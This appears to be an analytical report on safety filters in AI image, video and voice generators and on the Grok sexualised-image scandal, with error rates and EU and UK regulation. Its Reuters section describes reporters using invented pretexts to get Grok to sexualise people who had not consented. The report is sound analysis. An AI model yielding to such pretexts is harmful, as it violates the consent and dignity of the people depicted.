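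Sora's app and website closed on 26 April, according to OpenAI's *What to know about the Sora discontinuation*. Developers lost access on 24 September, and OpenAI's *Video generation with Sora* says there is no direct replacement. Sora's rules therefore no longer apply, although The Information's *OpenAI’s Plan To Revive Sora* has since reported that the company may bring it back.

### How often the filters were wrong

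Before launch, OpenAI tested Sora's output checks with thousands of prompts that testers had written to get around its rules. OpenAI ran the prompts through a version of the model without the usual refusals, graded the resulting videos, and measured how many harmful videos the checks blocked and how many harmless ones they let through. The table converts OpenAI's figures into error rates.

| Type of content | Harmful videos missed | Harmless videos blocked |
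|---|---:|---:|
| Nudity or sexual content, no one's likeness used | 4.0% | 3.8% |
| Nudity or sexual content using a likeness | 1.6% | 2.4% |
| Self-harm | 0.3% | 5.4% |
| Violence and gore | 4.9% | 3.0% |
| Prohibited political persuasion | 4.5% | 1.3% |
| Extremism and hate | 3.2% | 0.9% |

The self-harm checks missed the least and wrongly blocked the most, as one would expect if OpenAI had made them especially strict. They might block a film about recovery from an eating disorder, for example.

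Low error rates can still produce many wrongful refusals, because most requests are harmless. Suppose users make 100,000 videos and 1% of them break the rule on violence. At the rates in the table, the checks would block 951 of the 1,000 harmful videos and 2,970 of the 99,000 harmless ones, so about three quarters of the blocked videos would be harmless. The real proportion might be lower, since harmless videos from a test designed to provoke the filters are probably harder to judge than ordinary ones.

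The missed-harm rates may also overstate how much harmful content reached users, because they cover only the output checks, and the prompt checks would have stopped some requests earlier. The table shows how well the checks caught sexual videos that used someone's likeness, but not how often Sora recognised that an otherwise ordinary video showed a real person who hadn't consented, even though the consent rule mattered most for likeness. OpenAI also doesn't give the number of videos in each category, so readers can't calculate the margins of error.

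OpenAI's image generator, which is still available, has a similar design. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Images 2.0* describes classifiers that refuse some requests beforehand and a reasoning model that checks both the uploaded images and the result. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Images 2.5* reports what happened when testers tried to obtain prohibited images:

| Model | Safe image | Blocked | Harmful image shown |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
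| ChatGPT Images 2.0 | 75.2% | 23.1% | 1.64% |
| GPT-Image-2.5-Flare | 79.4% | 19.2% | 1.41% |
| GPT-Image-2.5-Sunburst | 77.0% | 21.9% | 1.09% |

The last column is a share of all prompts, most of which the models answered with a safe image, so it makes the filters look better than Sora's. Among the attempts that didn't end in a safe image, 4.7% got past the filters on Sunburst, 6.8% on Flare and 6.6% on Images 2.0. Flare's filters caught about the same share of these attempts as Images 2.0's, so Flare showed fewer harmful images because it produced safe ones more often.

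### Legitimate users whom the filters refuse

Posts on Google's developer forum show how wrongful refusals affect people's work. In *Request allowlist access for Veo on Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform*, a documentary company asks for permission to animate childhood photographs of the women in its film, who are now mothers and grandmothers. The company wants to show each woman as a child, sitting in the interview chair. The women could consent to this, but the filter detects only that the photographs show children.

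Another developer used Google's own image model to create pictures of family scenes for an advert. *Veo 3.1 image-to-video blocks wholesome commercial storyboard* reports that Veo refused to animate them, even after the developer removed every mention of children from the prompt. Veo did generate video from text alone, but the character looked different in each shot. The error codes match Google's filter for children, so Veo was applying the rule as written, even though the children weren't real. In *Request allowlist access for Veo person generation (minors)*, an animator asks for an exception for a clay-style cartoon child that couldn't be mistaken for a real one.

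A filter may block a real person's likeness even when that person has consented. *Licensed celebrity likeness blocked by "prominent individuals" filter* describes a developer who had a signed licence from an artist, but Omni still rejected the artist's photographs. *Request Allowlist Access for Veo 3.1* comes from a company that couldn't make training videos of its own founder, who had agreed to them. A photograph doesn't show whether a contract exists, so an upload check alone can't distinguish a licensed video from an impersonation. An allowlist can solve this, but someone at Google has to review each applicant's documents, and small studios may have to wait.

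Some refusals have no obvious connection to people. One user asked Omni to give a video a green tint and received a notice that the request was harmful, according to *Omni video editing instantly rejects harmless prompts in Flow and Gemini app*.

These are the users' own accounts, and people whose requests succeed have no reason to post, so the posts show that wrongful refusals happen and whom they affect, but not how common they are. Google's documentation for Veo and Omni describes the filters but doesn't give error rates like those OpenAI publishes.

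### Voice Engine and GPT-4o's preset voices

In March 2024, OpenAI announced Voice Engine, a model that could imitate a speaker from a 15-second recording, but gave access only to a small group of partners. Partners had to get the speaker's explicit consent and tell listeners that the voice was artificial, and they couldn't let their own users create voices. OpenAI said that any wide release should include a way to verify that speakers had knowingly added their voices, and a list of prominent people whose voices the system would refuse to copy.

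The restriction limited who could benefit from Voice Engine. One partner, a medical institute, used it to recreate the voice of a young patient who had lost her fluent speech because of a brain tumour. Her doctors took the sample from a video she had made for a school project. Other patients could have benefited in the same way, but only if their doctors had access.

GPT-4o, which OpenAI released in May 2024, posed a different problem because it generated speech directly. OpenAI's system card, published that August, reported that in rare cases during testing the model imitated the user's voice without being asked. A consent rule for users wouldn't prevent this, since the user hadn't requested the imitation.

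OpenAI therefore gave GPT-4o a fixed menu of voices recorded by actors, and trained the model to use them. While the model was talking, a separate classifier compared its speech with the selected voice and ended the conversation if they didn't match. This was easier than recognising celebrities, because the classifier needed only the selected voice as a reference and could reject a stranger's voice without having heard it before. Sora's checks had no such reference for an invented character, whose face could match anyone's, by accident or on purpose.

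In OpenAI's 2024 tests, the classifier caught every meaningful departure from the selected voice. Its precision (the share of its alarms that were correct) was 96% in English and 95% in other languages. These percentages aren't comparable with the last column of the Sora table, which gives the share of harmless videos that the checks blocked. These were internal results for the first version, so they are weak evidence about the voices in ChatGPT today.

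The classifier checked whether speech matched an approved voice, but not whether that voice should have been approved. In May 2024, OpenAI withdrew a voice called Sky after the actor Scarlett Johansson objected that it sounded like her. OpenAI said it had hired a different actor and hadn't meant to imitate Johansson. Sky was an approved voice, so speech that matched it would have passed the check.

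OpenAI later allowed some imitation of real speakers, but required stronger evidence of consent than it had for photographs in Sora. By early 2026, selected business customers could create a custom voice if they supplied a recording of the speaker reading a consent statement, though a convincing fake of the recording might get around this rule.

### Voices in video

Video generators now produce speech, so a limit on a separate voice product isn't enough. Sora's characters included a person's voice as well as their appearance. OpenAI scanned transcripts of generated speech, which can reveal a spoken threat but not whose voice is speaking. It also blocked attempts to imitate living musicians, but acknowledged that perfect protection for audio was difficult.

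Google avoids much of this problem in Omni by leaving features out. According to its August 2026 documentation, Omni doesn't offer voice editing, developers can't upload a voice recording for it to copy, and it ignores the sound in reference videos. Users can't add dialogue when they extend an uploaded clip of someone talking, though they can if Omni generated the original clip. A user therefore can't have Omni extend real footage of a politician's speech with invented remarks. The limits also prevent film-makers from using Omni to correct a misread line in their own footage.

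Google does allow copies of real voices in Google Vids, its video tool for office work. *Google Vids just became a far more capable video maker* (Bonggolto, 2026) reports that users can create an avatar of themselves from a selfie and a short voice recording. To prevent misuse, Google restricts each avatar to the account holder's own likeness. The founder whose photographs Veo rejected could presumably make an avatar this way from his own account, but his staff couldn't make one for him.

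## Grok's image editing: limits set after misuse

Google and OpenAI restricted the use of real people's likenesses before releasing their video and voice generators. In late December 2025, the social media platform X and its owner at the time, Grok's maker xAI, gave X's users a tool for editing photographs of real people. X added its main limits over the next 16 days, after the tool had produced millions of sexualised pictures.

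### From the editing feature to the subscription limit

Grok has a public account on X that people can tag in a post to ask a question or request a picture. The Independent reported that from 29 December they could also have it edit real photos. A user could ask Grok to remove a stranger's clothes in a photo, and Grok would post the result publicly.

Interest surged on 31 December, when xAI's founder, Elon Musk, shared a picture Grok had made of him in a bikini. Between then and 8 January, Grok posted more than 4.4 million images, about 14 times as many as in the previous nine days, according to a *New York Times* analysis by Conger, Freedman and Thompson (2026), *Elon Musk’s Grok A.I. Chatbot Made Millions of Sexualized Images*.

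Software that "undresses" people in photos already existed, but it had no comparable audience. The researcher Genevieve Oh followed Grok's account for 24 hours and found about 6,700 sexually suggestive or undressing images an hour. Five other leading websites for sexual deepfakes averaged 79 an hour (Nolan, 2026, *Lawmakers and victims criticize the choice to limit Grok’s AI image generation*).

xAI had already made sexual content part of its product. In August 2025 it gave Grok a "Spicy Mode" for adult material, TechSpot notes. This made the problem harder to fix. A company that bans all nudity can block any picture in which a classifier detects it. A company that allows some nudity also has to distinguish real people from invented ones, and people who have agreed from people who haven't.

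*Grok under fire for sexualizing women and children's images* (Fatimah, 2026) reports that by 3 January, Grok's account had posted that it had found "lapses in safeguards" and was urgently fixing them. The chatbot writes posts for that account, so the post is weak evidence of what xAI's engineers were doing.

On 9 January (8 January according to Conger and colleagues), X limited Grok's image generation and editing to paying subscribers. Subscribers have card details on file, so in theory they are easier to identify if they misuse the tool. Software enforced this limit, which restricted who could make pictures but not what the pictures could show.

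Conger and colleagues reported that the number of images fell significantly, presumably because most users don't pay. But the limit did little to stop determined abusers. Henry Ajder, a specialist in deepfakes, told Nolan that people can easily give false details or use temporary payment methods, and that identifying offenders helps only after they have made the image. Ashley St. Clair, a commentator whose photos users had turned into explicit pictures, said many of the accounts targeting her were already verified. The British government called the change "insulting" to victims because it turned creating unlawful images into a paid service.

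The limit also stopped people without a subscription from making harmless edits, such as brightening a family photo. Subscribers could still ask Grok to undress a colleague. The limit didn't cover Grok's website. Futurism (2026), citing *Wired*, reported that the site was still producing graphic sexual images of people without their consent, for free, on the same day.

### The block on revealing clothing

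Indonesia blocked Grok on 10 January, and Malaysia followed a day later. On 14 January, X announced two further limits, quoted in *Musk's xAI curbs sexually explicit image generation in Grok* (Kapoor, 2026). X said it had stopped the Grok account from editing images of real people to show them in revealing clothing such as bikinis, and had blocked users from generating images of real people in bikinis, underwear and similar clothes "in those jurisdictions where it's illegal". The table shows the scope of each limit.

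| Limit | Whom it restricted | Where it applied | What stayed open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Subscribers only, 9 January | Users without a paid plan | Grok's image tools on X | All edits by subscribers, and Grok's website |
| No edits of real people into revealing clothing, 14 January | All users, including subscribers | The public Grok account | Grok's separate app and website |
| No images of real people in bikinis or underwear, 14 January | All users in countries where such images are illegal | The Grok account and the Grok chat inside X | The chat inside X in other countries, and the separate app and website |

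A block by country depends on where the user is. If a woman lives in a country that bans these images, the block doesn't stop someone elsewhere from making one of her. X did not name the countries, so people couldn't easily check whether the block applied where they lived.

Blocking by country can still make sense as a response to national laws. When Ofcom (2026), the British communications regulator, opened its investigation of X, it explained that the UK's Online Safety Act doesn't require platforms to restrict what people in other countries can see. But the Act covers illegal images that people in the UK can see, wherever they were made, so X would also have to find and remove those made abroad.

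Conger and colleagues found that after 14 January, Grok's public account largely ignored requests for bikinis but still dressed people in leotards and one-piece swimsuits. Any rule about clothing has to allow some garments and forbid others, and users will ask for the most revealing ones it allows. The rule also restricts legitimate users, such as a swimwear shop that wants to show a model in next season's bikini, because X's statement made no exception for people who have agreed to the edit.

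The separate app and website were a larger gap because users could still generate sexual content there in private. Engadget's *Grok generated an estimated 3 million sexualized images* mentions reports that the app still produced images undressing real people. X may have dealt with its own platform first because private images don't reach the public unless someone shares them. Private images are also much harder for outsiders to count. Common Sense Media's *AI Risk Assessment* (2026) tested the app, the website and the X account separately, a sensible precaution when the chatbot's limits differ between them.

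### How many images Grok made

The Center for Countering Digital Hate (CCDH), a British nonprofit organisation, estimated that Grok produced about three million sexualised images in the 11 days from the feature's launch on 29 December to 8 January. It randomly sampled 20,000 of the 4.6 million images that Grok posted publicly on X and sorted them with the help of AI, according to MLex's *X's Grok chatbot generated 3 million sexualized deepfakes in 11 days* (2026).

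CCDH counted an image as sexualised if it showed a person in a sexual position, in revealing clothing such as underwear or swimwear, or covered in fluid meant to look sexual. The Decoder's *Elon Musk's AI chatbot Grok flooded X with millions of sexualized images* reports that 12,995 of the 20,000 images (65%) were sexualised, and that 101 of those appeared to show children.

To extrapolate, CCDH scaled these counts up to the full number of images. Its published totals imply a full count of about 4.62 million, so each image in the sample represents about 231 on X:

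- Sexualised images: 12,995 × 231 ≈ 3.0 million
- Sexualised images that appeared to show children: 101 × 231 ≈ 23,300

A different random sample would have given slightly different counts. For something this rare, the count typically varies by about its square root, or about 10 images here. The 95% range is roughly twice that in each direction, from 81 to 121 images, which scales up to between 19,000 and 28,000 on X. CCDH's published figure of 23,338 is more precise than the sample justifies. The larger total is much more precise relative to its size, because sampling error alone would move it by only about 30,000 either way.

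A bigger sample wouldn't remove classification errors. CCDH had to judge age from appearance, and a young-looking adult can pass for a teenager. If 10 of the 101 judgements were wrong, the estimate would fall by about 2,300. A CCDH spokesperson told South West Londoner that people had reviewed the sample by hand (*Concerns rise over online harm after data reveals scale of sexualised images*). That review should have caught some mistakes.

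CCDH also couldn't determine from the images whether the people in them had consented. Musk's bikini picture would meet its definition of a sexualised image, though he shared it himself. A finished image also doesn't reliably show whether the person is real or whether the original photo was already revealing. The three million figure is therefore an estimate of sexualised images, not of victims or non-consensual edits. It could also understate Grok's total output, because it leaves out anything users made privately in the app or on the website.

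X was slow to remove the worst material, sexualised images of children. On 15 January, 29% of those in CCDH's sample were still on the platform. That is only about 29 images, but if the sample was representative, several thousand were still on X.

Conger and colleagues used a different method and reached a lower figure. They used one AI model to find images of women and another to judge whether those images were sexual, and checked a selection by hand. They applied this to 525,000 images from 1 to 7 January and estimated that at least 41% of Grok's posts, or 1.8 million, were sexualised images of women. AI Forensics' *Grok Generating Flood of Sexualized Images of Women and Minors* (2026) gives a third estimate, based on how much clothing people were wearing.

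| Source | Images examined | What it counted | Share |
|---|---|---|---:|
| Conger and colleagues | 525,000 | Sexualised images of women | At least 41% |
| AI Forensics | More than 20,000 | People in minimal clothing | 53% |
| CCDH | 20,000 | Sexualised images of anyone | 65% |
| Oh | 24 hours of posts | Sexually suggestive or undressing images | 85% |

Most of these figures conflict less than they seem to. AI Forensics found that 81% of the people in minimal clothing appeared to be women, so about 43% of all the images showed women dressed that way, close to Conger and colleagues' 41%. Their totals cover only women, while CCDH's also include men and children. Oh's figure is the least comparable because it comes from a single day.

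AI Forensics also reported that 2% of the images showed people who appeared to be 18 or younger, four times CCDH's share. But the 2% includes images that weren't sexual, and the age estimates came from Google's Gemini model, so the difference doesn't mean that CCDH undercounted.

None of these counts can show whether X's later block worked, because they all cover images from before 14 January.

### Reuters' tests after the restrictions

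Reuters' *Despite new curbs, Elon Musk’s Grok at times produces sexualized images*, from 3 February, describes a more direct test in which nine reporters in the US and UK gave Grok photos of themselves and one another fully clothed. They asked it to show the people in sexually provocative or humiliating poses, using invented stories in which the subject had not consented. In one story, a London reporter told Grok that a shy colleague would hate to be seen in a bikini and that the picture was for an office joke.

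Between 14 and 16 January, Grok produced sexualised images for 45 of 55 prompts (82%), according to The Independent's *Grok generates sexualised images even when told subjects don’t consent*. In 31 of those 45 cases, the reporters had warned that the person was particularly vulnerable, and in 17 they had said that the images would be used to degrade them. Grok kept making images after a reporter in London said that a colleague had been abused as a child and, later, that he was crying over the pictures.

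Reuters contacted the companies and tested Grok again on 27 and 28 January. This time it produced sexualised images for 29 of 43 prompts (67%). Reuters couldn't tell whether xAI had changed anything. The results aren't enough to establish a change either, since chance alone would produce a difference this large in about one comparison in ten.

When Grok didn't comply, it often didn't explain why. In 24 cases across both rounds, it produced no sexualised image of the person, but it called the request inappropriate in only seven of them. In others it gave no response, showed a generic error, or produced pictures of a different, apparently invented person.

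The reporters also tried the same or nearly the same prompts on OpenAI's ChatGPT, Google's Gemini and Meta's Llama. All three refused every time, usually with a warning about consent. Chatbots at the time were therefore well able to prevent these images.

The test was easy for a safeguard, though, because Reuters stated explicitly in its prompts that the person hadn't consented, so Grok didn't have to infer this from the photograph. A user who lied about consent would be harder to stop. The results also don't show how many harmless edits the rival systems refuse.

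The tests are weaker evidence about the 14 January block because The Independent doesn't specify whether the reporters used X, the app or the website. It does report that Grok's public account had stopped producing sexualised images on the same scale, which suggests that the block had some effect there.

### How X and xAI responded

xAI sent Reuters and *Fortune* the same automated reply, "Legacy Media Lies". Neither company answered Reuters' detailed questions about the images or responded to Conger and colleagues.

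In its public statements, X mainly held users responsible. A spokesperson told reporters that X removes illegal content, permanently suspends accounts and works with governments and police. X said anyone who prompts Grok to make illegal content would face the same consequences as someone who uploads it. In January, X also said it had "zero tolerance" for child sexual exploitation and non-consensual nudity.

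Punishing users may deter some of them, but the comparison with an upload overlooks that Grok made the picture and posted it from its own account, whereas a platform only hosts what users upload. Stanford researcher Riana Pfefferkorn told *Fortune* that this was the first time a platform had itself generated non-consensual pornography on such a scale, and that it was unclear who would be liable.

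### Ofcom's investigation

Ofcom contacted X on 5 January and opened a formal investigation on 12 January. The Online Safety Act requires platforms to take proportionate steps to stop people in the UK from encountering illegal content, including intimate images shared without consent. Platforms must also update their risk assessments before making significant changes, and one of Ofcom's questions was whether X had done so. The investigation therefore covered the decision to launch the feature as well as the response to its misuse.

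Ofcom called X's announcement of 14 January "a welcome development" but continued its investigation. On 3 February it decided that xAI was outside its jurisdiction in this case, according to Digital Policy Alert (2026). Digital Watch's *Ofcom expands scrutiny of X over Grok deepfake concerns* explains that the Act covers a chatbot only if it lets users interact, provides search or produces pornographic material, and that many chatbots fall partly or wholly outside it. Ofcom is therefore investigating Grok on X, but not the separate app and website, which X's limits did not cover. In February and March, Ofcom's researchers tested X and Grok themselves, using accounts and devices that Ofcom controlled.

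Ofcom's *Investigation into X Internet Unlimited Company* (2026) says the regulator discovered that some accounts could reach pornography on X without proving that their owners were adults. X fixed this immediately. On 14 October, Ofcom narrowed the case to concentrate on illegal content, setting aside its questions about X's duties to children without making a finding. Ofcom says the flaw wasn't directly related to the reports about Grok, so the fix reveals little about the image limits.

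Nine months after opening the case, Ofcom had not yet decided whether there were reasonable grounds to believe that X had broken the law. If it finds such grounds, it must publish provisional findings and let X respond. It can then fine the company up to £18 million or 10% of its worldwide revenue, whichever is greater. In the most serious cases, it can ask a court to order internet providers to block a site.

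### The European Commission's case

On 8 January 2026 the European Commission ordered X to keep all its internal documents about Grok. On 26 January it announced an investigation under the Digital Services Act, an EU law that requires very large platforms to identify and reduce the risks their services create. The investigation was still open on 3 December.

A central question is whether X should have assessed Grok before anyone misused it. According to Vergnolle (2026), in *Grok is a Make-or-Break Test for the EU's Digital Services Act*, none of the three annual risk reports X had published under the Act mentioned Grok as a possible risk. One report classified the spread of child sexual abuse material on X as low risk. Vergnolle argues that X had to include Grok because it is either part of X or a related system. If the European Commission agreed, other platforms would find it harder to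 leave a built-in chatbot out of their reports.

### Whom the EU ban covers

The EU also passed a new law, the *Digital Omnibus on AI* (2026), which The Record describes as a response to the Grok episode. It amends the AI Act, the EU's main law on artificial intelligence. From 2 December 2026, it bans certain AI systems that make child sexual abuse material. The ban also covers certain systems that make realistic images, video or audio showing an identifiable person's intimate parts, or showing them in sexually explicit activity, without their explicit consent.

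The ban treats companies that supply AI systems, which the AI Act calls "providers", differently from those that use them. A provider may not offer a system in the EU whose intended purpose is to make such material. This rule covers "nudification" apps, which turn photos of clothed people into fake nudes.

General-purpose image generators have a different purpose, so the law applies a test with two parts. The system is banned only if both are true:

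1. Such material is a foreseeable result that users can reproduce without significant technical changes to the system.
2. The provider lacks reasonable and adequate safeguards to prevent it reliably and to correct misuse that it observes or that people report.

The 2024 AI Act defines a "deployer" as a person or organisation that uses an AI system, except for personal, non-professional use. A private individual who makes a fake nude of a neighbour therefore falls mainly under other laws, including criminal law. A deployer breaks the ban only by using a system for the purpose of making the prohibited material.

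The table applies these rules to some invented cases.

| Case | Likely result |
|---|---|
| An app that undresses people in photos without checking consent | Banned because of its purpose |
| A general image generator that makes nude pictures of real people on request and has weak filters | Banned because its safeguards are inadequate |
| The same generator with strong filters, which one user finds a way around | Allowed if the provider takes reasonable steps to correct the problem |
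| A company that uses a poorly protected generator to make landscapes | The company isn't in breach, though the generator's provider may be |
| A generator that puts a real adult in a bikini | Outside the ban if the picture shows no intimate parts or explicit activity |

### What safeguards the law expects

The law doesn't prescribe a particular safeguard, though its recitals give examples. Recitals are introductory explanations that guide courts but aren't binding by themselves. *The 47 recitals of the Digital Omnibus on AI* lists cleaning the training data, training the model to refuse, filtering prompts and outputs, restricting use, detecting abuse and acting on complaints. These examples include both instructed limits, such as refusal training, and software outside the model.

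According to the recitals, safeguards are adequate if they match the state of the art and demonstrably prevent the material or make it sufficiently unlikely. Safeguards therefore don't have to be perfect, but a provider needs evidence that they work. Error rates like those OpenAI published for Sora would be useful evidence. The state-of-the-art standard could also make it hard for a provider to defend a generator that complies with requests its main rivals refuse.

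Providers must also deal with foreseeable attempts to get around their safeguards. If they run the system through a website or platform, they can monitor misuse and respond. They have less control after releasing a model for others to download, and under the recitals this affects which corrections are reasonable.

A system intended to make intimate images can be legal if everyone it depicts has agreed. The provider needs a reliable way to collect and demonstrate their consent. A tick box where the uploader vouches for someone else, as Sora allowed for ordinary photos, probably wouldn't be enough.

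The bikini case in the table matters most for Grok, because the new law may not prohibit the kind of edit that X chose to block in January. The recitals exclude partly nude pictures of adults that reveal no intimate parts and show no explicit activity. Reuters didn't ask Grok for full nudity or explicit sex, so many of the pictures in its tests would probably fall outside the ban. CCDH counted swimwear and underwear as sexualised, so an unknown but possibly large share of its three million images would also fall outside it. Lawmakers made the exclusion because a wider ban could have affected clothing shops that let customers try on swimwear virtually.

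### Whether the EU needed a new law

Vergnolle questions whether adding provisions is the best response when regulators could enforce the existing ones more vigorously. The Digital Services Act already required X to look for risks in advance, and child sexual abuse material was already illegal. Vergnolle argues that if the Commission can't secure serious consequences in such a clear case, it will struggle with more disputed harms such as disinformation.

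Shultz, Heumann and colleagues (2026), in *Targeted and Ignored*, argue for going further. They searched 200 websites for the names of all 720 members of the European Parliament and found 50 depicted in, or associated with, sexual deepfakes. Of these, 46 were women, about one in six of the Parliament's women. "Associated with" is a broad category. The sites hosted manipulated sexual images of eight members, all women, and 22 members appeared on pages that linked to a nudification tool beside their biography or portrait.

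Shultz and colleagues argue that the EU's existing rules apply only after the harm is done, depend on victims to report it, and place the strongest duties only on the largest platforms, although most of the harm occurs on small sites, often based outside the EU. They also note that these rules set no fixed deadline for removing such images, while new US and UK rules require removal within 48 hours.

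Their first criticism doesn't fit X very well. The duty to assess risks is meant to be preventive, but it failed because X left Grok out of its reports and nobody made X add it in time. The case for enforcement is therefore strong for Grok on X, especially since the new ban probably leaves bikini edits to older laws. But the ban also covers small nudification sites, which the Digital Services Act's strongest duties don't reach, and it should apply to Grok's own app and website too.

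National authorities and the EU's AI Office enforce the new ban and can impose fines of up to €35 million or 7% of a company's worldwide turnover, according to the European Commission's *EU ban on AI ‘nudification' apps starts to apply*. People can also complain to the authorities or go directly to court. The Commission's guidelines on how the ban works are still a draft, open for comment until 8 January 2027. Soares (2026) had already raised doubts about enforcement in June, in *EU Lawmakers Move to Ban AI Nudifiers, but Enforcement Remains Unclear*.

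On 3 December, the day after the ban took effect, nine of the ten most popular nudification sites were still accessible in the EU, according to NewsIreland.EU's *EU bans AI ‘nudification’ but apps still online* (2026). One day is too soon to judge the law, but fines may have little effect on operators who are abroad and hard to identify. Shultz and colleagues therefore want legal duties for the businesses these sites depend on, including app stores, payment companies and web hosts. The Commission began by asking Google, Apple and Meta, on the day the ban took effect, what they were doing to keep nudification apps out of their app stores, search results and social networks.
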